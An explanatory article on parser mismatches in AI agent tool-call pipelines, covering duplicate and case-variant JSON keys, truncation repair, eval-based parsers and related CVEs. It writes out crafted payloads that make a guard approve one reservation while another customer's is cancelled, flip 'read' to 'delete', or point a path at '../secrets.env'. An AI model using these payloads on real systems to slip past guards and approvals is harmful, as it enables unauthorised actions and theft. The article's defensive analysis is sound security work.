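# When software reads an AI system's output differently: parsing mismatches and their security consequences

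## How one AI output comes to have two readings

A large language model produces text, so when developers connect one to other software to change a booking, edit a file or query a database, other programs have to turn that text into actions. Each program uses a parser, which converts text or bytes into a structure the program can act on. Two parsers can interpret the same bytes differently. Security researchers call this a parser differential and have found it over the past few decades in web servers, certificates and document formats. Work from 2026 documents it in the software around AI agents, where the program that approves an action and the program that carries it out often come from different teams and use different parsers.

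### The path of one tool call

*Oops!... I Parsed It Again* (Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz, 2026) uses a task from τ-bench, a benchmark for agents, to follow a request from the model to its effect. In the task, a customer asks an airline's AI agent to cancel reservation I3EHXC.

The model cannot cancel anything itself. The developer has given it a list of tools, and it answers with a tool call, a request to run a named function. Here the function is `cancel_reservation`. The arguments usually come as JSON, a text format that writes data as names (or keys) paired with values:

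`{"reservation_id": "I3EHXC"}`

Each tool also has a schema, a machine-readable description of the fields a call may or must contain. This tool's schema declares one required field, `reservation_id`, whose value is text. The harness is the program that runs the agent by sending text to the model and carrying out the model's tool calls. Each of the following programs may parse the call before the booking is cancelled.

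| Program | What it does with the call |
|---|---|
| Inference server or provider's API | Finds the call in the model's text and turns it into a tool-call object. Some APIs give the client the raw argument text, others an object they have already parsed. |
| Gateway | Translates between the formats of different model providers and writes the arguments out again. |
| Software kit (SDK) | Parses the provider's response inside the developer's program. |
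| Agent framework | Parses the arguments, looks up the tool and often checks the arguments against the schema. |
| Guard | Decides whether the call may run, and logs the decision. |
| Executor | Decodes the arguments into its own data structure and runs the tool. |
| Shell or database behind the tool | Parses the command or query into which the executor has inserted the reservation number. |

Few systems contain all seven, and a small script may have only an API, a software kit and the tool function. But repeated parsing is built into the design of many APIs. They deliver the arguments as a JSON document inside a text string, so every later program that needs the arguments has to parse them again.

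Of the components in the table, the guard and the executor matter most for security. The guard is the component or person that allows or denies a tool call before it runs. It may be a permission check in the framework, a gateway that enforces company policy, a filter that looks for secrets in outgoing text, or a person who clicks "approve". A human guard sees what one component has parsed and displayed, and so relies on that component's reading. The executor carries out the call. It is often a server that uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting AI agents to tool servers. Third parties write many of these servers.

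The seven parsers would agree on the line of JSON above, but they can differ on input that the format leaves open. Under the JSON standard, RFC 8259, the names in an object "SHOULD be unique", which is only a recommendation. If `reservation_id` appears twice, JavaScript keeps the last copy, some parsers keep the first, and others refuse the document. The standard decoder of the Go programming language also ignores case when it matches field names. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz call each of these choices defensible on its own, which seems right, but nobody required the programs in a chain to make the same choice.

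### What the call was meant to do

When two parsers differ, engineers can't settle the matter by checking which one matches the model's own reading, because the model has none. It emits a sequence of text fragments and has no internal JSON parser whose result they could look up. The user's goal is a poor substitute, because every bad choice by the model would then count as a parsing fault. Treating the provider's parse as authoritative only favors one parser over the others.

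*Do Tool Calls Execute as Intended?* (Yang, Li and colleagues, 2026) avoids both problems by defining the intended action as the action that the emitted call denotes under the tool contract. The paper uses "tool contract" to mean the rules for commands or arguments that the tool description gives the model. For a structured tool such as `cancel_reservation`, the action consists of the argument values, such as the reservation number I3EHXC. A shell command needs a longer specification, covering the program to run, its arguments in order, the operators that join commands, the working directory, the relevant environment settings and the standard input.

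The definition deliberately ignores whether the model chose well. Suppose the customer asks to cancel I3EHXC and the model writes another customer's booking number. The intended action is then to cancel the other booking, and software that does so has delivered the call correctly. Yang and colleagues count this as a generation error. They need to separate generation errors from delivery errors because a transcript records the call and its result, but not what each program in between received. In their production data, 95.1% of failures were attributed to the model when judged from transcripts alone, although the delivery path had caused more than half of them.

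Yang and colleagues describe the path from a model's call to the executed action as a series of hops. At each hop, one side writes the call out and the next side parses it. The path is sound when the receiver at every hop parses the intended action, and the first hop where this fails is the place to look for the fault. A changed call is one whose executed action differs from the intended one. In one of their examples, the model writes `console.log("test")`, but a hop parses the text a second time and strips the quotation marks, so the program receives `console.log(test)`. This is an instruction to print the contents of a variable named `test` instead of the word "test". Adding more quotation marks tends to move the damage to the next parse, so they send the code through a channel that the faulty hop does not parse, such as a file.

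The equation compares actions rather than text. Bash, a common command shell, reads `"a\b"` and `"a\\b"` as the same word. When Yang and colleagues used plain string comparison instead of the receiver's own parser, it flagged 15 of 35 unchanged pairs as changed.

The definition has a gap, though probably a small one in practice, because it works only when the tool description gives the call one meaning. If a call contains the same name twice, and neither the description nor the JSON standard specifies which copy counts, there is no single intended action for the later programs to match. Models do not seem to write such calls on their own. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz found no repeated name in the call itself in any trial where they could inspect the raw text. But an attacker can write them, so it helps to have a test that does not mention intention.

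### When two readings do harm

Ali and Smith's *A Survey of Parser Differential Anti-Patterns* starts from a simple model in which two parsers accept the same input language but build different structures from some valid input. Not all of the survey's examples fit this model. In one, the Zoom chat client and server both accepted a malformed character, but one parser read it as a single three-byte character and the other as three separate characters, so one program found a single message where the other found two. The fix was to add a missing validity check. Because the input was invalid, a useful definition has to cover any input both parsers accept, whether or not the standard permits it.

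For a tool call, the two parsers that matter most are the guard's and the executor's. Write *b* for the bytes of the call, *G*(*b*) for the guard's reading and *E*(*b*) for the executor's. A policy *P* answers "allow" or "deny" for any action put to it. The harmful case is the one where

*P*(*G*(*b*)) = allow, but *P*(*E*(*b*)) = deny.

Suppose a policy lets customers cancel only their own bookings. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz altered the bytes of a cancellation so that the guard read I3EHXC, the customer's own reservation, while the executor read U86B6B, somebody else's. The policy allows the cancellation that the guard read but would have denied the one that ran. The log recorded the guard's reading, so a later reviewer would have found an approved cancellation of I3EHXC and nothing wrong. The gap closes if the guard passes on the call it parsed and approved instead of the bytes it received.

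Many differentials fail this test. If two parsers keep different copies of a repeated comment field and the policy does not check comments, both readings get the same verdict. If the policy denies the guard's reading, nothing runs, and the worst outcome is refusing an acceptable call. If both readings are the same and the action is still harmful, the policy is at fault, and better parsing will not fix it.

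Whether a pair of parsers is dangerous therefore depends on the policy being enforced, so an auditor cannot judge the pair alone. Differences between the parsers matter more when the policy permits less. A person who approves "cancel I3EHXC" has authorised only that cancellation, so almost any difference in what runs bypasses their approval. A guard that allows everything cannot be bypassed in this sense.

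The formula also assumes that the guard and the executor receive identical bytes. If a program between them rewrites the call, the executor parses a different string, *b*′, and the question becomes whether the policy would allow *E*(*b*′). This often happens with shell commands, because several programs handle the text after approval.

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz give two parsers the same input and compare the results. To do this, they put each result into a canonical form, a single fixed way of writing a given piece of data. Theirs sorts the keys and labels every value with its type. They record a disagreement when both parsers accept the input but the results differ, and a split when one parser accepts it and the other rejects it. For example, two official MCP software kits split on the text `"12"` in a field that should hold a number, because one converts it to the number 12 and the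 other refuses the call.

A split, which looks like the milder problem, becomes a bypass when the guard lets through a call it cannot parse. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz leave splits out of their threat model when the only effect is denial of service, which is reasonable as long as the guard blocks any call it cannot parse. Some filters may instead let these calls through so that ordinary work does not stall. The policy then has no *G*(*b*) to evaluate, and the call runs anyway. Anyone auditing a connection therefore needs to know what the guard does on a parse error, and the remedy is to make it refuse the call.

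Differentials can also cause trouble without an attacker. Yang and colleagues examined production sessions of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, and found that it changed 12.0% of the Bash calls that carried code, escape sequences or long text. Most accidents of this kind cause a failed run or a wrong result. One could meet the harm condition by chance, for example if a mangled path pointed at a protected file, but an attacker deliberately searches for bytes that meet it. Ordinary traffic is therefore a poor guide to the risk of attack. In tests by Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz, no two components disagreed on the benign inputs, but most pairs disagreed on at least some of the crafted ones.

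### Who can put the bytes there

An attacker who knows of a useful disagreement between two parsers still has to get the right bytes to both. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz distinguish three positions from which an attacker could try to do this. They assume the attacker knows which parsers are in use, which is a fair assumption for open-source components.

The on-path attacker controls a component between the model provider and the agent, such as a gateway or proxy, and can rewrite the bytes of a call. If the attacker simply replaced one reservation number with another, a guard further along would read the new number and could deny the call. A parser differential gets the altered call past the guard. A program that parses the call and writes it out again will usually drop a repeated name, so an attacker who relies on one must alter the call after the last program that does this. A name in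 unusual letter case survives being parsed and written out again.

A tool-server attacker controls a tool's schema and description, for example through a malicious or compromised MCP server or a poisoned entry in a registry where developers look for tools. The attacker does not write the values in the call, but the schema determines which fields a validator accepts, and models tend to fill in the fields a schema declares. The attacker can therefore create a field that one component checks and another ignores.

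The content attacker controls only text that the model reads, such as a web page, a shared document or the response of an online service. This attacker has the least control but the easiest way in. The attacker's bytes reach the tool call only if the model copies them there, and the model may rewrite, decode or shorten them, or refuse. Whether the attack works depends partly on the model, so it has to be measured for each model and each way of serving it.

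An attacker can hold more than one position, as when the operator of a malicious tool server also writes a document that the agent reads. Results from one position do not carry over to another. For the reservation attack, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz fed the altered bytes directly to the guard to simulate a compromised gateway. Their test is good evidence about the guard and the executor, but it is not evidence that someone could cause the same flight cancellation by publishing a web page.

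### Older cases

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz call their attack tool-call smuggling, an allusion to HTTP request smuggling. HTTP is the protocol browsers use to request web pages. Large sites often put a front-end server in front of the server that processes requests, and the front end forwards many requests over a single connection. Both servers must agree on where one request ends and the next begins. *HTTP Request Smuggling In 2020* (Klein, 2020) recounts how Chaim Linhart, Amit Klein, Ronen Heled and Steve Orrin showed in 2005 that the two servers can place that boundary differently.

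*HTTP Desync Attacks* (Kettle, 2019) describes a request with the body `12345G` and two `Content-Length` headers, which state the body's length, one as 6 bytes and the other as 5. The front end uses the 6 and forwards everything as one request. The back end uses the 5, stops before the `G`, and treats that letter as the start of the next request. The next visitor's `POST` therefore becomes `GPOST`, which the server does not recognise. A stray letter is only a nuisance, but an attacker can instead leave the beginning of a whole request, which the front end never examined as a request. Refusing any message with two conflicting lengths removes this ambiguity.

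The 2009 case concerns the certificates that let a browser check that it has reached the right website. The attack uses the null character, a byte with the value zero, which marks the end of a piece of text in the C programming language. Someone who owns badguy.com requests a certificate for the name `www.bank.com[NULL].badguy.com`. The issuing authority reads the entire name, finds that it ends in a domain the applicant owns, and signs the certificate. Browser code that stops at the null reads only `www.bank.com`, so an attacker who can intercept the victim's connection can pose as the bank. Software can prevent this by refusing names that contain a null or by comparing names over their full length. Red Hat's *certs with nuls* (2009), a set of certificates for testing software against the flaw, credits Dan Kaminsky and Moxie Marlinspike with presenting it at that year's Black Hat conference.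 According to Route Fifty's *Digital certificate standard yields to hackers* (2009), they had found it independently.

The harm condition applies here unchanged. The authority is the guard, the browser acts on the result, and the policy is that only the owner of a domain may have a certificate for it. The policy allows what the authority read but would deny what the browser read.

These cases fall under Interpretation Conflict, an entry in the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), which is a public catalogue of the kinds of flaw that lead to vulnerabilities, maintained by the American non-profit MITRE. MITRE's *CWE-436* covers products that handle inputs or steps differently, so that one acts incorrectly because it misjudges the other's state. The entry locates the weakness mainly in proxies, firewalls and other intermediaries that, like a guard, allow, deny or modify traffic according to how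 they expect the client or server to behave. CWE 5.0, the October 2026 edition, also lists a narrower class under this entry, CWE-1471, Insufficiently Controlled Parser Differential.

The parent class, MITRE's *CWE-435*, covers components that each behave correctly alone but go wrong together. A note in the entry limits the term "interaction error" to products that follow their specifications and points to CWE-436 when one of them does not. Tool-call mismatches can be of either kind. A parser that keeps the last copy of a repeated name breaks no rule of JSON, but the Go software kit for MCP did break a rule by ignoring letter case, because the message format beneath MCP prescribes exact field names. *CVE-2026-27896 Detail*, the entry for that flaw in the US government's vulnerability database (NVD), lists it under CWE-436 and gives version 1.3.1, which matches case exactly, as the fix. MITRE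 acknowledges that the distinction is unclear where standards are missing or widely ignored. It also discourages using CWE-435 for individual vulnerabilities, so in practice an auditor's report will cite CWE-436 or its newer child.

The Go kit's maintainers adopted a different parser, but Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz report that it ignored a null character after a field name. A later version of the parser fixed this too. Null characters, which had misled browsers in 2009, were still causing programs to read the same input differently in 2026.

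### Two neighbouring problems

Parser differentials are easy to confuse with prompt injection, in which instructions hidden in a web page or document lead the model to make a call that the attacker chose. The resulting call may be well formed, and every program on the path may read it the same way. In the terms used above, the intended action is the attacker's, and *G*(*b*) and *E*(*b*) both match it. A guard with a sound policy has a fair chance of catching such a call, because the guard reads the call that will run. With a parser differential, the guard can approve one action while a different one runs, even if the model made no mistake. A defence that looks for malicious instructions in the model's input may find none, because an on-path attacker does not need any.

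The other, broader related category is *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, an entry in a list of risks by the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP). It covers insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's output before it goes on to other systems. In one of its scenarios, a user of a chat-like feature asks for a database query that deletes every table, and the application runs the query without checking it. The database executes the query as the model wrote it, so there is no parsing mismatch, but the application should not have run it. Ordinary remedies apply, such as restricting what the database account may do or checking the query first.

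Momot, Bratus and colleagues make a similar distinction for software in general, between checks that cannot properly validate a program's assumptions about its input and components that interpret the same input differently. OWASP's category covers both, but most of its examples, including model output passed straight to a command shell, involve missing or inadequate checks. Adding a missing check can introduce the second kind of fault. A filter that searches a command for a forbidden word is a crude parser, and its reading of the command can differ from the shell's.

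## Turning a model's text into a tool call

In the airline example, the model outputs a series of whole numbers. Each number stands for a token, a fragment of text such as a word, part of a word or a punctuation mark. The inference server, the program that runs the model, converts the numbers into text, searches the text for a tool call and builds the tool-call object that later programs receive. The guard receives only that object, so it cannot distinguish the server's mistakes from what the model wrote.

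### From token numbers to text

A tokenizer converts text into token numbers for the model, then converts the model's output numbers back into text, mostly by looking them up in a table. The model learned during training to use each number in a particular way, but the table is stored in an ordinary text file beside the model, and anyone with write access can edit it.

NVIDIA's *Secure LLM Tokenizers to Maintain Application Integrity* shows what such an edit can do. In the tokenizer for BERT, an older language model, "deny" is number 9772 and "allow" is 3499. If an attacker changes the file so that 9772 prints as "allow", every later program receives "allow" when the model's output was "deny". Common loading software does not enforce a one-to-one match between strings and numbers, so two strings can share a number, and it is then undefined which one the decoder prints.

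Someone who can edit this file, its cached copy or its source repository can probably do plenty of other damage, so this is a supply-chain risk rather than something a content attacker could exploit. NVIDIA recommends pinning and auditing the tokenizer's version and checking the file when the program loads it, because an attacker may have pointed the program at a different cache. Text-only logs may not reveal the change, so an investigator also needs the token IDs.

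Even with an intact tokenizer, the server's decoding choices can change the text that the parser receives. Many models reserve certain numbers, called special tokens, for structure such as the start of a reply, and decoders often have an option to omit these from the text. If the model marks its calls with special tokens and the server omits them, the parser finds no call. Streaming, in which the server sends text as the model produces it, can also cause errors. A single accented letter or Chinese character may take more than one token, so a server prints damaged characters if it decodes each token separately instead of waiting for the whole character.

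### Finding the call

Developers train each family of models to write tool calls in a particular format, often with a marker before and after the call. The marker may be a special token or a run of ordinary characters. A special token is safer if the server looks for its token ID. In decoded text, the special token looks the same as ordinary tokens that spell it out, so a parser that searches the text cannot distinguish them.

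Text that only quotes a call can therefore be run as one. Suppose a customer asks the airline's agent how cancellations work, and the model answers with a sample call, including the markers. One parser would display the sample, while another would cancel the booking. The same could happen when a model quotes a web page that contains a call in the right format. The guard's ownership check won't stop the cancellation if the customer owns the booking in the sample. Matching markers by token number prevents this confusion in formats that use special tokens. For other formats, the server can at least restrict where in a reply a call may appear.

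A related flaw from 2026 in vLLM, a widely used open-source inference server, affected text on its way into a model. Corgea's *vLLM Vulnerable to Remote DoS via Special-Token Placeholders* reports that if the server ran a model that handles images as well as text, a user could crash a worker process by typing the placeholder for a special token as ordinary text. vLLM's developers have since changed the code. Tokenizers can avoid this kind of mistake by never turning a user's text into a special token's reserved number.

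Some models write calls as Python code without any marker, for example `[cancel_reservation(reservation_id="I3EHXC")]`. vLLM recognised these by their shape, using a regular expression (a pattern for matching text). A reply that opened with such a list only to illustrate the syntax would have the same shape as a real call. Corgea's *vLLM has a Regular Expression Denial of Service (ReDoS, Exponential Complexity) Vulnerability* reproduces the pattern, which was so deeply nested that matching certain text took exponentially long. GitLab's *CVE-2025-48887* (2025) records that this let an attacker stall the server, and links to the code change that followed. A parser that reads the text once from left to right does not have this problem.

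### Extracting the name and the arguments

After finding the call, the server has to separate the tool's name from the arguments. Models write arguments in three main styles, and the parser has to resolve some ambiguity in each.

| Style | A count of twelve | What the parser may have to settle |
|---|---|---|
| JSON | `{"count": 12}` | Which copy of a repeated name counts |
| XML-like | `<count>12</count>` | Whether 12 is a number or text, and where a value ends if it contains a tag itself |
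| Python-style | `count=12` | Which Python expressions count as values, and what to do with a repeated argument |

JSON distinguishes the number `12` from the text `"12"`, but XML-like formats usually don't, so the parser has to look up the type in the tool's schema. If the schema gives no type, the parser has to guess. When a model writes a long value into an argument, such as a web page, the value may contain the tag that closes the argument, and a parser that stops at the first match will cut the value short.

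The server then usually writes the arguments out again as JSON, which hides how it parsed the original text. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz could see the raw argument text for only three of the ten models they tested (the two OpenAI models and Llama-4-Scout). For the other seven, the API had already parsed the call or a router had rewritten it. Someone auditing a system built on one of those services can check the values that arrive but cannot tell whether the model wrote the call correctly or an earlier program repaired it.

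### Repairs and cut-off calls

A model generates its output one token at a time, and ordinary generation doesn't guarantee valid JSON. The model may add a comma after the last field, use the wrong quotation marks, put a sentence before the object, or reach its length limit before the closing brace. A strict parser rejects all of these, which annoys developers when a person could easily see what the model meant, so many libraries repair the text before parsing it.

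Streaming is another reason to parse leniently. An interface that shows arguments as they arrive has to parse an incomplete document, so a partial parser supplies the missing punctuation. This works well for a progress display but causes problems when another component treats the result as the finished call.

Some repairs to a model's output are safe enough. If a model wraps a complete JSON object in formatting marks, software can remove them without changing the arguments. But if a value is unfinished, completing it is a guess, because the missing part could have been almost anything.

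Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz cut argument documents at ten points and gave the pieces to six parsers. One cut fell inside the number 12, leaving:

`{"action": "read", "count": 1`

The partial parser in LangChain, a popular framework for building agents, closed the object and returned a count of 1, a value the model never sent. Another framework's lenient parser passed the unparsed text on as a string. The paper does not name that framework because a report to its maintainers is still open. Python's standard parser in its strict configuration and two Go decoders rejected the input.

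When a parser repairs truncated JSON, numbers are especially prone to unnoticed errors because JSON doesn't mark where a number ends. A truncated string lacks its closing quotation mark, but a 12 cut off after the first digit looks the same as a complete 1. The only sign of the error is the missing closing brace, which the repair adds. File paths can fail in a similar way if the parser also closes unfinished strings. A request to delete `/data/reports/old` could become a request to delete `/data/reports`, which is also a valid path.

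A cut-off call can also get past a guard. Suppose the policy allows a count of up to 10 and the model is sending 12. If the guard checks the stream after only the first digit has arrived, it approves a count of 1, and the executor later receives 12. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz tested truncation only on individual parsers, so they showed that parsers read cut-off calls differently but did not demonstrate a working bypass. They advise checking streamed arguments only once they are complete, and for that the harness needs the reason the stream ended. Many APIs report whether the model finished or reached its length limit. If a connection closes without such a report, the harness should treat the call as unfinished.

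Even a call that arrives in full can come out differently when the server streams it. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz gave vLLM 0.32.0's parser for Python-style calls this input:

`tool(path="report.pdf", path="../secrets.env")`

When the parser reads the whole response at once, it keeps the last path, `../secrets.env`. In streaming mode, it produces `report.pdf.env`, which appears nowhere in the input.

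The splice comes from how the parser sends updates. Each time more text arrives, it writes the call out again as JSON and sends only what it hasn't already sent. When the second path arrives, the client has a partial JSON object ending in `report.pdf`, but the new version has `../secrets.env` in the same position. The result is consistent with measuring the difference by character count. `report.pdf` and `../secrets` are both ten characters long, so the parser treats the first ten characters of the new path as already sent and adds only `.env`.

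This method assumes that new text only extends the old, and a repeated argument breaks that assumption. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz did not report the fault to vLLM, because no model they tested repeated an argument in the raw text they could see, and an attacker who can insert one in transit already controls the call. Those are fair reasons to treat it as a low-priority security flaw, but the mechanism remains fragile. A parser could reject the repeated argument, as Python does when it compiles such a call, or stop with an error whenever the new version no longer begins with the text already sent.

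### When parsing runs the text

A few parsers have run the model's text as code. One was vLLM's parser for Qwen3-Coder, a family of coding models that write arguments in an XML-like format. When the parser could not find an argument's type, it passed the text to Python's `eval()`, which runs a string as Python code. This is a convenient way to convert types, since it turns the characters `12` into a number and `[1, 2]` into a list. But if the text contains a call that runs a system command, `eval()` executes it too.

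The flaw, CVE-2025-9141, affected versions 0.10.0 and 0.10.1, and version 0.10.1.1 fixes it. *PYSEC-2026-2014* (2026), a later entry for the same flaw in OSV's database of open-source vulnerabilities, lists three conditions for an attack: the operator must have enabled tool calling and selected this parser, and the argument's type must be missing or unrecognised. An authenticated user who can get the model to put code into such an argument can run that code on the server. Red Hat's *CVE-2025-9141* rates the impact "Important" rather than critical because the attacker needs valid login credentials.

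Xinference, another inference server, had a similar flaw without that protection. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-61539* (August 2026) describes how versions up to 2.5.0 passed the text of Llama 3 tool calls to `eval()`. Anyone who could send the server a request could steer the model's output with a crafted prompt, without logging in. The entry gives the flaw the maximum severity score of 10. Version 2.7.0 fixes it.

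*CVE-2026-61539* (Hatagale, 2026) quotes the call `eval(model_output, {}, {})` from the Xinference code. The two empty pairs of braces give the evaluated code no variables from the surrounding program, but they don't isolate it, because Python still supplies its built-in functions, including the one that loads other modules. A parser that needs only numbers, strings, lists and similar values should use a function that accepts nothing else, such as Python's `ast.literal_eval`.

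A guard placed after the inference server cannot prevent this kind of attack. The code runs while the server is still parsing the model's text, before there is a call for the guard to approve or deny.

LangChain had a different problem, in how it saved and reloaded data. When the framework writes one of its own objects to JSON, it includes a key named `lc`, which marks the object for the loader to rebuild. Its writing functions, `dumps()` and `dumpd()`, did not escape ordinary dictionaries (Python's structure for names paired with values) that contained the same key. The loading functions, `load()` and `loads()`, therefore treated those dictionaries as LangChain objects, even though the program had saved them as plain data.

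A model's reply could supply the dictionary. LangChain's advisory, reproduced in GCVE's *GHSA-C67J-W6G6-Q2CM* (2025), names two fields of extra information attached to a reply, `additional_kwargs` and `response_metadata`, as the most common route. An attacker could influence these fields through prompt injection, and some of LangChain's streaming features would then save the reply and load it again. An application could therefore be vulnerable even if it only loaded data it had saved itself.

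The marker could also indicate a stored secret. By default, the loader then looked up a named environment variable, where programs often keep passwords and access keys, and put its value into the result. The security company Cyata (2025), whose researcher found the flaw, also identified a permitted class that made a network request as soon as the loader created it, so an attacker could receive a secret without seeing the model's reply. Cyata found no way to run arbitrary code through `loads()` alone, but reported that code could run if the application later rendered a template the attacker had supplied.

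NIST lists this flaw as CVE-2025-68664, confirms the missing escape, and gives 0.3.81 and 1.2.5 as the fixed versions. The writing functions now wrap any plain dictionary that contains `lc`, so the loader treats it as data. LangChain also tightened the loader. By default, it rebuilds only objects from the core package, blocks one type of template that can run code, and no longer reads secrets from the environment.

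The stricter default did not apply throughout the framework. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-44843* (2026) covers older LangChain code that could call the loader with `allowed_objects="all"`, which overrides the default. Attackers could then revive any object that LangChain trusts, far more than that code needed, though they could not create arbitrary Python objects. Versions 0.3.85 and 1.3.3 fix this. An application's own code can also override the new default, so it is worth searching for such calls after an upgrade.

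### Generating only valid text

A server can prevent the model from writing invalid JSON instead of repairing it afterwards. Providers call this structured output or strict mode. Before generation starts, the server turns the tool's schema into a grammar, a set of rules for which text may follow which. At each step, the model assigns every token a probability of coming next. The server uses the grammar to find the tokens that could still lead to a valid document, sets the probability of all others to zero, and picks the next token from those that remain.

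Write *p*(*t*) for the model's probability of token *t*, and *A* for the set of tokens the grammar allows at this point. The server then chooses with the probabilities

*p*′(*t*) = *p*(*t*) / Σ*p*(*u*) for *t* in *A*, and *p*′(*t*) = 0 otherwise,

where the sum runs over every token *u* in *A*.

For `cancel_reservation`, the grammar requires an opening brace, then the name `reservation_id`, a colon and a quoted string. After the colon, the model might give a probability of 0.7 to a digit, 0.2 to a quotation mark and 0.1 to a closing brace. Only the quotation mark is valid there, so its probability rises to 1. The check has to cover every character in a token, because the first may be allowed when a later one is not.

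If the model finishes normally and the server implements the schema correctly, the result has the declared fields with the declared types. If the grammar lists each field once, the model cannot repeat one. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz found that OpenAI's strict mode also stopped models from leaving out optional fields.

Strict mode does not make the values correct, since a wrong reservation number is also valid text. It may even hide missing information. If the customer never gave a number, a model that has started the call must still fill the required field, and a made-up number has the same form as a real one. The grammar also doesn't enforce the structure of JSON inside a string, so if a tool expects a whole settings file in one text argument, that argument can contain almost any text.

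Even in strict mode, a call can be cut short if the model reaches its length limit. The text so far is then the valid beginning of a document, and a lenient parser may complete it incorrectly, as LangChain's did with the 12.

The guarantee also ends when the text leaves the provider. Strict mode restricts only what the model generates, so it doesn't stop a gateway from rewriting the arguments later, and programs after the gateway can't tell from the bytes alone whether the model produced them. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz similarly point out that if a malicious tool server adds a field to its schema, strict mode will make the model fill it in as the schema specifies.

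Strict mode accepts only some schemas. In the same tests, OpenAI's strict mode and Google's Gemini each rejected all 80 requests that used `oneOf`, a keyword that requires a value to match exactly one of several schemas. OpenAI's default mode accepted them. A developer may have to simplify the schema to use strict mode, and the tool then has to check any rules the simpler schema omits.

The server also has to parse the tool's schema. GitLab's *CVE-2025-48944* (2025) records that vLLM did not validate a schema's `pattern` and `type` fields before processing them. One request with a malformed field could crash the worker process, which stayed down until someone restarted it. An agent that passes on schemas from third-party tool servers could trigger such a crash even if the user meant no harm. vLLM's developers have changed the code, and an agent can also validate each schema when it first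 connects to a tool server.

### Rejecting, repairing or asking again

Strict mode reduces the number of malformed calls, but the harness still needs a rule for those that arrive. Rejecting them is the simplest choice, and it prevents the harness from running an action that came from the parser rather than the model. The step then fails, and the harness has to tell the model, or the agent may tell the customer that a booking is cancelled when it is not. With current commercial models, rejections may be rare. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz collected 1,120 sets of arguments from six such models, and the defence they recommend, which parses each call only once, blocked none of them. Those were short calls to four simple tools, so a coding agent that writes whole files into its arguments will probably have more calls rejected.

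Repairing the text avoids the delay but may cause the wrong action to run. The damage is easier to contain if one component repairs the text before the guard checks the call, and every later component uses the repaired version. The guard then at least checks the action that will run, and the log can record the repair. If the guard and the executor each repair the text with their own library, they may complete it differently, which creates a new parser differential.

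The harness can also send the error back to the model and ask for a new call. This takes more time and money, and it may not help. A call that was too long for the limit will be cut off again unless the harness raises the limit or the model writes something shorter. The new call may be for a different action, so the guard has to check it from scratch, and a person's approval of the earlier version should not carry over. If the first reply contained several calls and some have already run, the harness must not run them again.

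It makes sense for most agents to repair only the wrapping around a complete call. If the call itself is malformed or cut off, the agent can ask the model again a fixed number of times, then reject the call if none of the retries is valid. The display code can still use partial parsers, since briefly showing a count as 1 before it becomes 12 does no harm there.

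## Checking a tool call's JSON arguments before it runs

The guard and the executor can read different arguments from the same tool call, even when the call is complete and its JSON is valid. The JSON standard leaves several decisions to whoever writes the parser. Other decisions arise after parsing, when a program compares the arguments with a schema or matches an approval to a call. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz examined these decisions for tool calls and built attacks that exploit several of them.

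### Repeated names

Suppose the airline's agent sends this cancellation:

```
{"reservation_id": "I3EHXC",
 "reservation_id": "U86B6B"}
```

If a tool call's JSON arguments give a name the value I3EHXC and then repeat the name with the value U86B6B, some parsers keep the first value and others keep the last. Bray (2017), in *The JavaScript Object Notation (JSON) Data Interchange Format* (RFC 8259), writes only that the names in an object "SHOULD be unique". He warns that software receiving repeated names behaves unpredictably, and that some programs return every pair.

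In an earlier blog post, *JSON Lesson* (2013), Bray guessed that the most common behaviour was to keep the last copy, as JavaScript's rules require. But Hatlen reported in *Use last-wins strategy for duplicate keys in JSON objects* (2017) that the MySQL database kept the first. At that time, a check that ran in MySQL and a tool written in JavaScript would have read the two lines above as different bookings. In the same year, according to Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz, two parsers in the CouchDB database resolved a repeated name differently, which let users make themselves administrators.

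The simplest remedy is to reject JSON objects with repeated names. IETF's *The I-JSON Message Format*, a stricter profile of JSON, forbids them. When Go's developers discussed a new JSON decoder, they noted that Bray himself recommends this profile and that security tools have trouble checking what an object means if its names repeat. Their new decoder rejects repeated names by default. Python's standard parser keeps the last value unless the developer supplies a function that raises an error.

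### Names that nearly match

Two names can also differ slightly and still count as the same name for one of the parsers:

```
{"reservation_id": "U86B6B",
 "Reservation_ID": "I3EHXC"}
```

A parser that requires exact names reads U86B6B and treats the second line as an unrelated field. Go's older decoder, `encoding/json`, ignores letter case when it matches names to the fields a developer has declared in a structure. It stores U86B6B, then overwrites it with I3EHXC because `Reservation_ID` matches the same field.

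cyberphone reported this behavior in Go in March 2016 (*encoding/json*), and Go's issue tracker labels the report as a security matter. Trail of Bits' *Unexpected security footguns in Go's parsers* (2025) lists the old decoder as ignoring case and keeping the last copy of a repeated name by default, while version 2 does neither. Developers can turn case-insensitive matching back on in version 2, but according to Go's *Package json*, that option also ignores dashes and underscores, so a guard's author should leave it off.

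A null character at the end of a name can have the same effect. JSON writes this character as `\u0000`:

```
{"action": "read",
 "action\u0000": "delete"}
```

Most parsers return `read` as the action and treat the oddly named second field as separate. Version 0.5.3 of segmentio/encoding, another JSON library for Go, treats both names as `action` and keeps the later value, `delete`. Version 0.5.4 returns `read` as the action.

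### The reservation attack in full

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz used this difference in letter case in the reservation attack described earlier. Their guard parsed calls with Go's older decoder, while the executor was the server side of an official MCP software kit, which requires exact names. They withhold the kit's name while a report to its maintainers is open.

The attacker first looks for an argument that decides the guard's verdict. Here it is `reservation_id`, because the guard allows a cancellation if the customer owns the booking. The attacker then puts the victim's booking under that exact name and the customer's own booking under `Reservation_ID`. The customer's booking must come second because Go's decoder keeps the last match. If the order were reversed, the guard would read the victim's booking, U86B6B, and deny the call.

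A compromised gateway replaces the model's call with these bytes. The guard parses them, reads the booking number as I3EHXC, confirms that the customer owns that booking, and approves the call. It logs an approved cancellation of I3EHXC. The executor parses the same bytes, reads the number as U86B6B, and passes that to the tool. The benchmark's tool checks only that a booking exists, so it cancels the other customer's reservation and refunds $1,203.

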